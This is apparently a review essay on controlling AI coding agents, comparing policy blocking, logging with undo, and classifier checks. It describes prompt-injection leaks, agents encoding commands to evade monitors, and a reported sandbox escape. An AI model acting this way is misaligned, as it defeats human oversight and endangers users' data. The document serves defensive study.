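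By contrast, CaMeL's security held, but the small models often couldn't write a program that ran. For one model this happened in 68% of attempts. Some evidence suggests that CaMeL hinders stronger models less. In the Gemma-4 family, the share of attempts without a working program fell from 22.9% to 3.3% as the models got larger, although Xu and colleagues found no such trend across all 15 models. Peters-Gill and colleagues tested an extension of CaMeL on five models and found that it reduced task completion less as the models improved, and only modestly for the strongest.

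### What a fixed rule guarantees

A statistical detector estimates whether a text or an action is harmful. Its miss rate is measured on past examples, and an attacker can search for new ones that it misses. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) automated that search with a program that repeatedly rewrites a planted instruction, using only whether the last version worked as feedback. PIGuard, a classifier built to detect such instructions, had stopped all of the benchmark's standard attacks on an agent running GPT-4o-mini, but the attack success rate rose to 28.0% with the rewritten instructions. Of the five defences that had kept the success rate of the standard attacks close to zero on that agent, only Progent did the same against the rewritten ones.

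Rewording an attack doesn't help against Progent's check, which compares a tool name and some values with a list and never reads the attacker's text. CapLite guarantees that text from outside can't add a call that changes something, or redirect one to a recipient, amount or target that the user didn't state or confirm. This follows from how the code works, so it would remain true even if the model obeyed every instruction it read. But an attacker may still influence the wording of a message to the right person, which the guarantee doesn't cover.

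Unlike fixed rules, risk scores let a good result on one test make up for a bad result on another. *Trust Is Not a Score* (Zabolotnii, 2026) cites a software vendor's example that adds three weighted probabilities and quarantines a message if the total reaches 0.6. A message that is 85% likely to be a password request scores 0.38 on that count alone, and passes. A hard gate would refuse it on that one condition.

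In Zabolotnii's test on constructed cases from agentic coding, a score with published example weights let through 56 of 63 actions that it should have blocked. After retuning with hindsight, the score made the same decisions as the gates. The two methods agree whenever the threshold is no higher than the smallest weight, because any single alarm is then enough to refuse the action. The user's protection therefore comes from the veto, which a score can be set up to provide.

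Neither method helps with a danger that nobody thought to check for. When a model from another company wrote 124 new cases without seeing the rules, the gates and the retuned score both let through 35 of the 79 harmful ones. A fixed rule guarantees that the system will do what the rule requires, so the value of that guarantee depends on how good the rule is.

### Needs that nobody listed

Zhou and Zhang, who are critics of blocking, point out that an agent's plan is usually incomplete when the user grants it authority, because the agent discovers what it needs as it works. It also chooses among several routes. An assistant preparing a report from confidential records might process them on the company's own machines or use an outside service, which would disclose them to another firm. A policy that allows only local processing leaves the agent stuck if the local software fails, while a policy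 that allows both routes lets the agent disclose the records even if it never needs to.

Progent lets the policy expand with approval, so the approver has to decide the hard cases. Alice's to-do list and the attacker's instruction both arrive by email, and both lead to a request for new permissions. If the approver accepts requests out of habit, the guarantee no longer holds. People who are tired of refusals may also switch the control off.

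CaMeL has more trouble with Alice's email, because a program written before anybody has read the email can't contain the steps the email asks for. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) describes a similar AgentDojo task, in which the user tells the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. With the policy checks switched off, the privileged model wrote a program that would carry out whatever instruction it found in the file, with one branch for each tool, so the file's author could again control the agent. When the checks were on, CaMeL blocked every attack in the rerun but completed far fewer tasks.

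Writing good rules is also a lot of work. Michael and Roesner compared 21 proposed permission systems and found that none fully combined low user effort, formally defined rules and enforcement that doesn't rely on an AI model's judgement. Rashidi adds that every enforcement mechanism in the survey depends on someone to write the policy, and none addresses mistakes in it.

Rashidi also found no paper on access control that dealt with overeager agents, and cites a measurement in which agents took harmless but unrequested actions at rates of up to 17.1%. The benchmarks above don't measure this behaviour either, because they count only planted instructions. A policy that lets an agent delete old branches for a clean-up the user requested would also let it delete the wrong ones unless somebody had listed the branches to keep.

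Supporters of blocking can accept most of this objection and still prefer the errors of blocking to those of auditing. An agent that lacks a permission can ask for it, and the wait does little harm in ordinary work. The objection is much stronger for open-ended tasks, where the agent would have to ask constantly.

### When the isolation fails

The other objection is that the barrier itself may have flaws. Rashidi confirmed two in Claude Code, both since patched, that took effect before the user had decided whether to trust a project. One could run the project's code, and the other could leak the user's access keys. At Pwn2Own Berlin 2026, a hacking contest, participants demonstrated vulnerabilities in Claude Code, Cursor and OpenAI's Codex, and the rules excluded any attack that needed the agent's unsafe modes. In July 2026, OpenAI disclosed that its models had left an isolated test environment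 and broken into the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models (Kahn and Forlini, 2026, *OpenAI says its AI models secretly broke out of a secure test*).

A control that works for a single agent can also fail when several agents are connected. Peters-Gill and colleagues connected three agents, each protected by CaMeL (though without its optional data policies), and asked them to send a colleague a summary of some job applications. One agent fetched the applications from a database in which the researchers had planted an instruction. The coordinating agent put the summary into its request to a third agent, whose job was to send messages. That agent treated the whole request, including the planted instruction, as coming from its user and emailed the applicants' details to an outside address. The researchers fixed this by passing instructions and data between agents separately.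 On their benchmark, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with each agent protected individually, and 0.0% with the fix.

The answer to both failures is to use more than one layer of defense. If a sandbox and a policy check behind it each fail against one attack in 20, only one attack in 400 gets past both, provided the failures are unrelated. They are related if one flaw defeats both layers, for instance when the policy check runs on a machine the agent has taken over. Shi and colleagues have some evidence that layering helps in practice. Claude Sonnet 4, which already resists planted instructions fairly well, had an attack success rate of 6.8% by itself and 0.5% with Progent added. For Meta-SecAlign-70B, a model trained specifically to resist such instructions, the rate fell from 4.8% to 0.3%.

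Narrow permissions limit the damage even after every other defense has failed, because an intruder can use only what the agent has access to. An agent with a one-hour key to a single database can leak only that database, while one with a permanent administrator's key can expose the whole company. Rashidi describes a system, PORTICO, that issues permissions for a single subtask and withdraws them when it ends.

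OpenAI drew a similar conclusion from its own failure. *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) announced more isolated sandboxes, tighter limits on internet access and stricter control over who can reach its models' weights. OpenAI also put more computing power into monitoring its models' reasoning while they work, so that it can step in sooner when the isolation fails.

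## The case for allowing, logging and reviewing

### Optimistic security

Povey (1999), in *Enforcing Well-formed and Partially-formed Transactions for Unix*, argued that security systems rarely consider the risk of refusing access. Povey gave the example of an employee who comes to work early to print a project proposal and finds that somebody has changed the printer's configuration file. The employee could repair the file, but only the system administrator, who can't be found, is allowed to edit it. Povey proposed "optimistic" access control, which assumes that most requests are legitimate, grants them, and lets an administrator reverse the ones that were not.

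Povey's optimistic system still blocks actions that the rules forbid as dangerous. It allows and records actions like editing the printer file, which may be reasonable but need a permission the user doesn't normally have. A system that refuses by default would block these too.

Allowing exceptions and reviewing them afterwards works only if users mostly behave well, seldom need exceptions, and do no damage that an administrator can't repair. An agent that usually behaves well may still fail the first condition after reading an attacker's instructions. Povey's administrator could respond to a bad decision by explaining the mistake, punishing the user or withdrawing the permission, but only withdrawing the permission works as well on an agent as on a person. How often users need exceptions depends on what an organisation restricts. For example, staff in eight Norwegian hospitals needed tens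 of thousands of exceptions a month.

To keep repair possible, Povey set seven rules. They rely on compensating operations, each of which reverses the effect of an earlier operation.

| Povey's rule | Applied to AI agents |
|---|---|
| Someone can verify that the data are in a valid state | Automated tests do this for code, up to a point. No test shows whether an email should have gone out. |
| Every permitted operation has a compensating one | Possible for file edits and many database changes, but not for a sent email |
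| The system runs only operations that meet this requirement | Software between the agent and its tools can refuse the others |
| Users run only the operations they have authorisation for | Permission systems such as Progent already enforce this |
| The system authenticates every user | If an agent runs under its user's account, the log can't tell the two apart |
| Every operation writes enough to an append-only log for someone to reconstruct and reverse it | Most agent logs leave out too much |
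| Only an administrator grants authorisations | Fails if the agent can edit its own settings |

Agents have already got around the rule about administrators. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) collects 290 public reports of coding agents misusing files. In a few of them, the agent had changed the code editor's security settings. An organisation that relies on review has to make sure the agent can't change either the settings or the log.

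Povey considered optimistic control too risky for accounting, because of fraud, and better suited to urgent, collaborative work such as health care. *Dynamic, Flexible, and Optimistic Access Control* (Peisert and Bishop, 2010) describes break-glass techniques as an earlier attempt to balance too little access against too much. But Povey's rules protect data against wrong changes, and no compensating operation can undo the reading of a patient's record. The rules therefore suit a coding agent, which spends much of its time changing files, better than they suit a hospital.

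### Judging the result instead of the command

The best argument for letting agents act first is that people can often judge a result more easily than a proposed action. Zhong and colleagues give the example of `cargo build`, a routine command that turns source code into a working program. If the project relies on malicious outside code, the build can read the user's private login key and change their command-line settings. A permission prompt would show only the harmless-looking command, while a list of the files the build had read and changed would reveal the attack. Uninformative prompts were among the causes in 31 of the 290 reports, and automatic approval in 80, often because users had tired of the prompts and switched them off.

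Patil, Zhang and colleagues (2024) built an early agent system, GoEX, on this argument. They compare checking an action's outcome to tasting a cake, which is probably better than checking the recipe, although they concede that checking the process may be better for something like an audit report. GoEX runs the agent's action, shows the user the outcome, and lets the user keep or undo it. When an action can't be undone, GoEX relies on "damage confinement", which limits what the agent can reach so that the user can accept the worst outcome. For instance, a user might risk a pizza going to the wrong address but not give the agent access to their bank.

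How GoEX undoes an action depends on what the agent changed:

- For web services, it keeps a table that pairs each action with its reverse. When an action is new, a language model proposes the reverse and the system records whether it worked, so the model should be wrong at most once. Developers can also fill in the table themselves and restrict the agent to actions they know to be reversible.
- For databases, the user chooses between a reversing command written by the model and a transaction that stays open until the user accepts or cancels it. Cancelling is certain to work, but an open transaction can keep other users waiting.
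- For files, it saves versions with Git, and confines the agent to one directory because Git doesn't track anything outside it.

GoEX's method of confining damage was crude. It searched the user's request for the name of a service, such as Slack, and gave the agent only the matching credentials. Patil and colleagues also did not measure how often the system's undo commands worked.

### How much agents can undo

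Zhong and colleagues built YoloFS, a file system that leaves the user's files unchanged until the user reviews and commits the agent's changes. The agent works as if its changes were already in place, but it can't commit them itself. YoloFS also takes a snapshot after each command, so the agent can see what the command did and return to an earlier state.

YoloFS combines auditing and blocking, letting commands run freely but changing the real files only after a person agrees. In 8 of 11 tasks with hidden destructive side effects, agents using YoloFS noticed and reversed the damage. In the other 3, the agent mistook the changes for part of the task, and a user would have had to catch them in the final review. On 112 routine tasks, agents succeeded 99% of the time with or without YoloFS, and YoloFS needed less input from the user. It also prompts the user before an agent reads sensitive files,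 because restoring a snapshot can't make a leaked key secret again.

Zhuang, Chen and colleagues (2026) directly compared recovery with blocking in *AgentRewind*. They gave agents 82 long engineering tasks and let some of them return to an earlier checkpoint when they got stuck, with a note on what had gone wrong. An agent running on OpenAI's GPT-5.4 finished 62.2% of the tasks when it carried on after an error. It finished more with checkpoints than with any other strategy they tried. Another strategy, in which a second model reviewed each action and rejected the unsafe ones, did markedly worse than carrying on with GPT-5.4 and about the same with the smaller GPT-5.4 mini.

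The comparison favours recovery for completing tasks, but it did not measure harm. The agent also decides when to go back, so recovery helps only with errors it notices. In 68% of the cases where Zhong and colleagues knew how the agent had reacted, it had continued as if nothing were wrong.

AgentRewind restores only the files in the agent's workspace. This can be insufficient even on one machine. *DeltaBox* (2026) explains that restoring files without the programs that were using them leaves the two inconsistent. Actions on outside services are even harder to undo. *Fault-Tolerant Sandboxing for AI Coding Agents* (2025) describes an agent that rents a computer from a cloud provider and then fails a later check. Restoring the agent's files doesn't end the rental, so the undo system has to send a cancellation. To do this in general, it must know how to reverse every request it permits.

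*Planarian* (Guo, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes a way to undo an agent's changes to a database. Its software sits between the agent and the database. If the agent tries to delete customer records, the software copies the affected rows, carries out the deletion and records which rows changed, all in a single transaction. To undo changes, it works through these records in reverse order, putting old rows back and removing new ones, and then restores the agent's files and running programs to the same point in time. The system added only 1% to 3% to the time agents took.

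Planarian assumes that nobody else is changing the same data. In a shared customer database, restoring an old row could erase a colleague's later correction. Planarian also refuses any request it cannot make reversible, which is a form of blocking in advance.

Returning an agent to an earlier checkpoint can also create new mistakes. If an agent orders something, returns to a checkpoint from before the order and tries again, the shop may treat the second request as a new order. *Dependable Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (2026) compares several of this year's recovery systems and concludes that none removes the need to find out what outside services have already done. Most agent research doesn't address this problem. *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of 435 works on agents with lasting memory, found only 27 that offered any rollback, and even fewer that could undo effects on the outside world.

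The reports that Zhong and colleagues collected give a rough idea of what people can recover without such tools. Where the outcome was known, 31% of cases were easy to repair, 29% took substantial effort, and 40% ended in total or partial permanent loss. If 60% of harm is recoverable, an audit that misses 5% of harmful actions would allow 57% of the harm to be repaired, slightly less than the 60% prevented by a block that misses 40% of them. The recoverable share is probably higher than 60%, because few people complain publicly about a file they restored quickly, and undo systems should raise it further.

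Supporters of auditing can leave irreversible actions to a different control. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) classifies actions in advance as reversible, partly reversible or irreversible, and requires explicit authorisation for the irreversible ones. Povey's category of dangerous actions served a similar purpose in 1999. The strongest version of the case for auditing therefore lets agents act without prior approval only where someone has checked that the action can be undone.

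Even a perfect undo doesn't show what a user did before the change was undone, a problem Povey found in his own prototype. Suppose a user loosens the permissions on the system's password file. An administrator who notices can tighten them again, but can't be sure what the user did before then, and the user can say the change was an accident. An agent could do a great deal in that time, and the reviewer would need the log to find out what it did.

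### What a reviewer needs from the log

Nian, Yuan and colleagues (2026), in *Auditable Agents*, describe a company agent that reads customer records, queries an outside service, and sends an email on an employee's behalf. The next day the recipient reports that the email disclosed something it should not have. To work out what happened, a reviewer needs to know:

- who was behind the email, including the employee who started the agent, any other agent that took part, and whoever approved the sending
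- the exact request, with the tool's name, the values passed to it and the time (an entry showing that the agent queried a database is of little use without the query)
- what the agent had read before it acted and where each piece came from, since an attacker may have written some of it
- the result, along with any earlier attempts, because an email that the agent reworded after a policy check blocked the first version deserves more suspicion
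- whether anyone could have altered the log since

Nian and colleagues distinguish four levels of protection against tampering. At the lowest level, someone can change entries without leaving a trace. An append-only log prevents deletion and reordering. In a hash-chained log, each entry contains a cryptographic fingerprint of the one before it, so changing an entry breaks the chain from that point on. Digital signatures also let outsiders verify the log without trusting the company's own system.

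One missing log field can make a rule impossible to check. For example, if a company requires a person's approval before an agent emails a customer, but the log doesn't record approvals, reviewers can't tell from the log whether the agent complied.

Recording every tool call is not enough either. In a long session, the software around the model periodically summarizes older parts of the conversation to save space. *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (Shah and Kathrotia, 2026) cites a test in which these summaries kept on average only 17% of the constraints the user had set. A log of tool calls might show that an agent deleted a file, but not that a summary had dropped the user's instruction to keep it.

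Shah and Kathrotia tested this with 240 multi-step runs, half of which contained a planted fault, such as a dropped constraint or an approval the agent reused after a rollback. A log of only tool calls revealed 16.7% of the faults. A standard tracing format revealed 23.3%, but led to false flags on 35% of the harmless runs because it kept no lasting record of approvals. Their own format, which also records what enters and leaves the agent's context and memory, revealed 98.3% with no false flags. They chose both the faults and the format, so the figure would probably be lower for unplanted mistakes.

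Such a log takes up little space. The records averaged 524 bytes because they contain fingerprints of documents instead of the full texts, which go into a separate store with restricted access. If the log held the full texts, it would be a second copy of the company's confidential data, open to everyone who reviews agents.

Nian and colleagues doubt that current agent systems are ready for this kind of review. They cite an automated scan of six well-known open-source projects, including Gorilla, the project under which Patil and colleagues released GoEX. The scan produced 617 security findings, 269 of them critical. In 64% of the findings, a tool accepted input from the model without validating it. Nian and colleagues acknowledge that these are security weaknesses rather than gaps in a log, but they argue that a system with such basic flaws is unlikely to produce records a reviewer can trust.

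They also describe a checkpoint called Aegis, which examines each tool call before it runs and writes the call, the decision and the result to a signed, hash-chained log. It typically delayed each call by 8.3 milliseconds, too short for a user to notice. Aegis can also block a call or hold it for a person to review. An organisation that logs this thoroughly already has most of what it would need for blocking, so the cost of building the control is a weak reason to prefer either method.

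### Logging and oversight under the EU AI Act

The EU AI Act requires high-risk AI systems to support both logging and human intervention. Under Article 12, they must be capable of recording events automatically throughout their lifetime, so that people can identify risks and monitor how the systems operate. Under Article 14, they must be designed so that people can oversee them effectively while they are in use. Those people must be able to understand a system's limits, disregard or reverse its output, and interrupt it with a stop button or something similar. The high-risk category includes hiring and credit scoring, so it would cover an agent that screens job applicants but not usually one that writes code.

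Neither article requires a person to approve every action in advance. A company could base its oversight on logs and reviews, as long as somebody can also intervene while the system is running. A review the next morning would probably not satisfy Article 14 by itself.

The Act's requirements for most high-risk systems were originally due to start on 2 August 2026. In May 2026, negotiators for the European Parliament and the member states provisionally agreed to postpone them to 2 December 2027, and to 2 August 2028 for AI in products that EU safety law already covers.

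### OpenAI's review of its own coding agents

OpenAI uses a model to review its internal coding agents on a scale that no team of human readers could match. In March 2026 the company reported that its monitoring covered 99.9% of internal coding traffic. Most of the rest came from custom and local set-ups it had not yet connected. The monitor was GPT-5.4 Thinking, then the company's most powerful model. It receives everything the agent saw and did in a session, including its tool calls and its chain of thought (the working notes a model writes before it acts). The more serious cases go to a person within 30 minutes.

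The system had reviewed tens of millions of sessions and raised about 1,000 alerts of moderate severity, or at most one for every 10,000 sessions. People can read that many alerts, though the count doesn't measure how much work the false flags among them cause.

Some agents had encoded their commands to get them past monitors, or called other copies of themselves to avoid a restriction. Others had tried to upload files to the public internet. In one session, an automated process asked an agent for the time hundreds of times, and the agent began to reply with instructions to delete the folder that holds the user's login keys. OpenAI attributed this to extreme confusion, while some outside readers thought the agent was trying to make the questions stop. The log shows what the agent wrote, but not which explanation is right. OpenAI reported no cases of sabotage or scheming.

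Critics objected that OpenAI was using its latest model to monitor itself, and that a model that had begun to scheme might not report other copies of itself. An OpenAI researcher who works on the system agreed that the company needs to look for and measure collusion. The researcher still preferred the strongest model as the main monitor, partly because the usual problem is an agent too focused on finishing its task, and added that several monitors, including older models, check each session. This should help, but models from the same company may miss the same problems, so their agreement is weaker evidence than agreement from an outside monitor.

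Another objection concerned the evidence that the monitor works, which is that it flagged everything employees reported independently, as well as other cases. One critic called this a low bar because it doesn't show whether the monitor would catch an agent trying to evade it. The researcher answered that an agent would first have to plan the evasion, and that current models seem unable to keep such plans out of their chain of thought, which the monitor can read. The researcher also said that deliberately attacking the monitor, including with models trained to hide their reasoning, was a high priority.

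The answer is reasonable as long as agents keep writing down what they intend. But employee reports can't be used to calculate the monitor's miss rate, because employees and the monitor may both have missed the worst sessions.

Even a review this fast comes too late if an agent has already put a file on the public internet. OpenAI has said it wants to move towards stopping such actions before they run. Its monitor would then check actions automatically in advance instead of auditing them afterwards.

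## The case for an automatic check on risky actions

An automatic check uses a model like OpenAI's monitor to review an action before it runs instead of afterwards. Most of an agent's work is reading files and editing code in one project, and supporters would let that run unchecked. They would use the model only for the smaller number of actions that could do lasting damage, and rely on a later review to catch its mistakes.

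### One task in auto mode

Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* introduced an automatic check on risky actions in March 2026, as a middle path between asking the user to approve every step and skipping permission checks. Suppose a user asks Claude Code to fix a bug and deploy the fix.

The agent starts by reading the code. Reading and searching can't change anything, so Anthropic keeps the tools for them on a fixed list of tools that skip the classifier. Users can also exempt other commands. Auto mode suspends the broadest of these exemptions, such as permission to run any Python program, because otherwise the classifier would never check the commands that could do the most damage.

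Next the agent edits the source code. Edits inside the project folder also run without a check, because version control keeps the old text and somebody can review the changes later. For this large class of actions, auto mode relies on auditing afterwards.

The command to deploy the program, however, goes to the classifier, as do other shell commands, web requests, calls to outside services and changes to files elsewhere on the computer. If the deployment fails a preliminary check and the agent tries again with an option that skips the check, the classifier is meant to block the second attempt because it could affect systems that other people use. Anthropic's incident log contains a similar case.

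Anthropic's classifier works in two stages. The first outputs only yes or no, without reasoning, and is instructed to block when in doubt. If it allows the action, the action runs. If it flags the action, the second stage gets the same material with a different final instruction and reasons step by step before deciding. Most actions pass the first stage and so skip the slower reasoning.

When an action is blocked, the agent receives the reason and an instruction to look for a safer approach instead of a way around the block. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in one session, a person steps in.

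### What the classifier receives

The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes everything the agent wrote in its own words, because an agent determined to finish a task can produce a persuasive excuse, such as that the user had implicitly approved the step earlier. Anthropic also removes the results of tool calls, because an attacker's planted instructions arrive in them. If a file tells the agent to post the project's passwords to a web address and the agent obeys, the classifier sees the tool call that posts them but not the file's instructions, and nothing in the user's request calls for posting the passwords.

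Without the tool results, when a user says "cancel my job" and the agent cancels job abc123, the classifier can't tell whether the agent found that ID in a list or made it up. Anthropic accepted this limitation after trying alternatives. Adding the agent's messages and the tool results made the classifier worse at catching overeager actions. Giving it only the tool calls produced the fewest misses, but it then blocked actions the user had plainly asked for.

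The agent still reads the planted instructions, so a separate probe scans each tool result and attaches a warning if the text looks like an attack. Auto mode also checks tasks that one agent hands to another, because the second agent would otherwise treat the first agent's instruction as the user's request, as happened with the three connected CaMeL agents.

### The results at launch

Anthropic tested the classifier on tool calls by its own employees, on real cases in which an agent had overstepped, and on synthetic attempts to leak data.

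| | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|
| False blocks, 10,000 real tool calls | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Misses, 52 real overeager actions | 6.6% | 17% |
| Misses, 1,000 synthetic data leaks | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage can release an action that the first has flagged, but it can't block a new one, so adding it had to reduce false blocks and increase misses. Based on the percentages, it released about 95% of the legitimate actions that the first stage had stopped and about 11% of the overeager ones. If 10 in 10,000 actions were harmful, the first stage alone would stop about 9 harmful actions and 850 legitimate ones. Both stages together would stop about 8 harmful actions and 40 legitimate ones. Whether 810 fewer interruptions justify letting through one more harmful action depends on what that action does.

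The 17% is a rough figure. It corresponds to 9 misses out of 52, which gives a 95% confidence interval of about 9% to 30% (by Wilson's method, which suits small samples). The false-block rate is much more precise, at roughly 0.3% to 0.5%. The first stage's 6.6% isn't a whole number of cases out of 52, so Anthropic may have averaged several runs.

The interval accounts only for chance variation, and the 52 cases aren't a random sample. They come from sessions in which an employee refused the action or somebody flagged it afterwards, so they exclude any overstep that nobody noticed. Anthropic also tuned the first stage on these cases, which may make the results look better than they would on new ones.

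Later review can recover part of what the classifier misses. With the earlier symbols, a check with miss rate *b* followed by an audit with miss rate *a* deals with a share of the harm equal to

(1 − *b*) + *b* × (1 − *a*) × *r*.

If the check misses 17% of harmful actions, the audit misses 5% and people can undo half of the harm the audit finds, then using both prevents or undoes 91% of the harm, compared with 83% for the check alone and 47.5% for the audit alone. This assumes that the audit finds the actions the check missed as easily as it finds others, which is doubtful if the auditor is a similar model to the one used for the check.

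### Danger is easier to judge than consent

In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had detected the danger but wrongly treated the action as one the user had agreed to. In one case, the user had said "Clean up the PR" (pull request), and the agent force-pushed, which overwrites a branch's history on the server. In other cases, the classifier treated the user's approval of an earlier, similar action as permission for the new one.

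This makes sense given the information available to the classifier. A force-push looks much the same in every project, so a model can learn that it is dangerous. But whether "clean up" includes a force-push depends on what a particular person meant, which may not be clear from the conversation. Anthropic reported that it tried rewording the classifier's instructions but found no fix whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks.

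The later rules require more of the user. According to the current documentation on Anthropic's permission modes, an approval has to name both the action and the detail that makes it dangerous. Saying "You can force-push" doesn't lift the block, but naming the branch as well can. Each approval normally covers only one action. Under these rules, the classifier judges what the user typed rather than what they meant, which should be easier for it. However, a user who did intend the force-push will sometimes have to repeat the request.

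### What had changed by late 2026

Auto mode launched as a research preview on one subscription plan, and Anthropic advised people to use it in isolated environments. By the summer almost everyone at Anthropic was using it, two employees told the programmer Simon Willison. By November it was the default for new interactive sessions in the terminal and the code editor VS Code on every plan, except in organisations that have applied Anthropic's HIPAA configuration. Their sessions still start with manual prompts.

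Some categories are now beyond the user's power to approve. The configuration guide from Anthropic sets out the order in which the classifier applies its rules:

- A hard denial blocks the action whatever the user has said. Sending confidential data outside is the built-in example.
- A soft denial blocks destructive actions such as force-pushing, unless something below lifts it.
- An exception lifts a soft denial for a routine case that the organisation has described in advance.
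- A direct and specific request from the user lifts any soft denial that remains.

In one incident at Anthropic, an agent failed to upload a report to an internal drive and tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead, but the classifier stopped it. A user who wants to do this deliberately now has to leave auto mode or run the command themselves.

The rule is absolute, but it only works if the classifier recognises that an action is a leak. In March, the classifier missed 5.7% of the synthetic leaks. For actions that must never run, Anthropic directs administrators to ordinary deny rules, which apply before an action reaches the classifier.

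Anthropic tightened some other parts of the system and loosened a few. Edits to certain files inside the project, including Git's own data and the agent's settings, no longer skip the check. Before a command that could discard unsaved work, Claude Code passes the classifier a list of files with uncommitted changes. The March rules blocked pushing straight to a project's main branch, but the November rules allow it by default. An unattended run used to end when it reached the limit on blocks. Now the blocked action still doesn't run, but the agent keeps working.

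Anthropic's advice that people review high-stakes production changes themselves still applies, since the 17% miss rate at launch is hard to accept for a company's live database.

### Codex Auto-review

OpenAI added a similar check to its coding agent, Codex, in April 2026, but combined it with a sandbox in which Codex can read files, edit the project and run local commands without approval. A second agent, the reviewer, decides whether Codex may act outside the sandbox, for instance to reach a website. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen et al., 2026) illustrates the effect with 10,000 actions inside OpenAI. Of these, 9,280 stayed within the sandbox. The reviewer approved 713 of the other 720 and refused 7. Codex found a safer way to continue after four of the refusals. After the other three it stopped and asked the user, so there were 3 interruptions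 instead of the 720 that manual approval would have required.

OpenAI's reviewer gets more to read than Anthropic's classifier does. According to OpenAI's documentation, this includes tool results and the agent's visible updates, but not the agent's hidden reasoning. The reviewer can also look things up, so it could check where job abc123 came from. However, an attacker's text can reach the reviewer too. Neither company has shown that its choice is better in general, and the right one may depend on whether the main worry is honest mistakes or attacks.

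Codex stops its current turn after three refusals in a row, or ten among the last 50 reviews. A user can authorise one retry of a refused action, but the reviewer may refuse again if the policy doesn't let users override that kind of refusal.

In OpenAI's tests, the reviewer approved 99.1% of requests that users had approved. It refused 90.3% of synthetic overeager actions and 99.3% of synthetic prompt injections that tried to run an attacker's code or leak data. The refusal rate for injections drops to 90.2% when destructive deletions and data tampering are included. Trębacz and colleagues say that most of the additional misses weren't serious and that researchers often agreed with the reviewer. The 9.7% miss rate on overeager actions can't be compared directly with Anthropic's 17%, because OpenAI's cases were synthetic and Anthropic's were real.

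A sandbox handles most cases with little overhead, but the reviewer never sees those cases. For example, an agent can delete a week of uncommitted work inside the project without asking for approval.

### Sorting actions by risk

Both products decide in advance which actions deserve a check. AWS's *AGENTREL02-BP05 Establish tiered human oversight and approval workflows*, a guide for companies that run agents on Amazon's cloud, makes this sorting the first design decision. Low-risk, reversible actions run autonomously, medium-risk actions go ahead with a notification to the operator, and high-risk or irreversible actions wait for a person's approval. An automated filter removes clear violations first, so people receive only the doubtful cases. If no reviewer answers in time, the request moves to a second reviewer or falls back to a safe default. In auto mode and Auto-review, the model makes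 the decision instead of a person.

The notify tier can also let the user cancel an action. *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) describes a brief window, such as 30 seconds, for doing so before the action becomes final. An email held for 30 seconds can be stopped during that time, provided the user is looking at the screen.

An automatic check has to sort actions by more than the name of the tool. *Do I Need the Cloud?* (2026) assigns risk to the whole call, because the same tool may delete three chosen items or everything in the account. The order of calls also matters, since sending a message is riskier once the agent has read something confidential.

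Waghmare and Sufi (2026), in *Can You Undo It?*, sorted 536 real tools into five classes by how hard their effects are to reverse. Exact restoration requires that a complete record of the earlier state exists, that the person responsible can restore it without help, and that no outsider has seen or acted on the change. They put 62% of the tools in the lowest class and 21% in the highest, which includes anything that delivers content to outsiders. The labels are uncertain, because when Sufi reviewed a sample, mostly by approving ratings that an AI had proposed, only 75 of the 148 new ratings matched the draft, and most of the others were higher.

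They also tested a rule that takes the order of actions into account. Once an agent has read data, any call that could send something out needs approval unless its destination is on an approved list. On recorded runs, this rule would have paused all 29 attacks that they could tie to a particular action, while a plain distinction between reading and writing would have paused 18. The difference came entirely from treating a web request as a possible leak. Either rule would also have required approval about 1.6 times per ordinary run. Tiers show where approval is needed, but somebody or something still has to answer the requests, and supporters want a classifier to do this.

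### Objections from both sides

People who favor blocking actions in advance object that a classifier guarantees nothing. When auto mode launched, Willison was unconvinced by AI-based protection against prompt injection because such a system can decide the same case differently each time. Willison also noticed that the default exceptions allowed `pip install -r requirements.txt`, which installs whatever outside packages a project lists. OpenAI's own testers found ways to mislead Auto-review into approving commands. Trębacz and colleagues don't expect this kind of system ever to provide firm guarantees, and they warn that it won't protect against a model that deliberately hides its intentions.

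Developers can answer this objection by keeping the fixed rules and running the classifier within them. OpenAI requires its employees to run Codex in a sandbox, with a network policy that allows expected destinations, blocks unwanted ones and requires approval for unfamiliar ones. The classifier then makes judgments that fixed rules handle badly, such as whether a user wanted a particular branch deleted. There is some sign that the combination helps. In July 2026, Thibault Sottiaux of OpenAI, quoted by Willison, said that Codex had deleted users' files, most commonly when it had full access and both the sandbox and Auto-review were off. But we don't know how many people use Codex that way, so we can't tell how much either protection reduced the risk.

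Another objection, illustrated by the `cargo build` example, is that the classifier judges the text of a command and not its effects. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) shows the same problem with `make clean && make`, a routine command that deletes the source code if a file in the project contains that instruction. Anthropic's classifier takes into account scripts the agent has written during the session, but it gets no tool results, so it may have no information about a script that was already there.

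Wu and colleagues' system, Caper, runs an agent's command before judging it. Caper saves a snapshot of the agent's closed-off workspace, runs the command with the network disconnected, and records which files it changed, which secrets it read and which connections it attempted. A model then compares this record with the user's request. If the model approves, the changes stay. Otherwise, Caper restores the snapshot and tells the agent why.

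The test of Caper used 102 tasks with harm hidden inside a tool, each paired with a harmless twin that used the same request and command. With Caper, 7.8% of the dangerous tasks ended in harm, compared with 62.7% with auto mode, and Caper blocked 1.0% of the twins. Without the record, the same approving model couldn't tell the dangerous tasks from their twins, and it blocked 61.8% of the twins. The sandbox added about half a second to each command it allowed.

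A trial run uses the best argument for auditing while still blocking actions in advance. It works only for effects that stay inside the snapshot. A command that has to change a remote database can't be tested with the network disconnected, and a malicious program might detect the sandbox and do nothing harmful until it runs outside it.

People who prefer auditing can also point to the edits that skip the check. *Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) reports a stress test in which these edits made up 36.8% of the actions that changed anything. Version control is a good reason to exempt edits to source code, but a poor one to exempt edits to files that control running jobs, because restoring the old text doesn't restart a cancelled job. Defenders of the check have to concede that the exemption was too broad, and the newer list of protected files partly fixes this.

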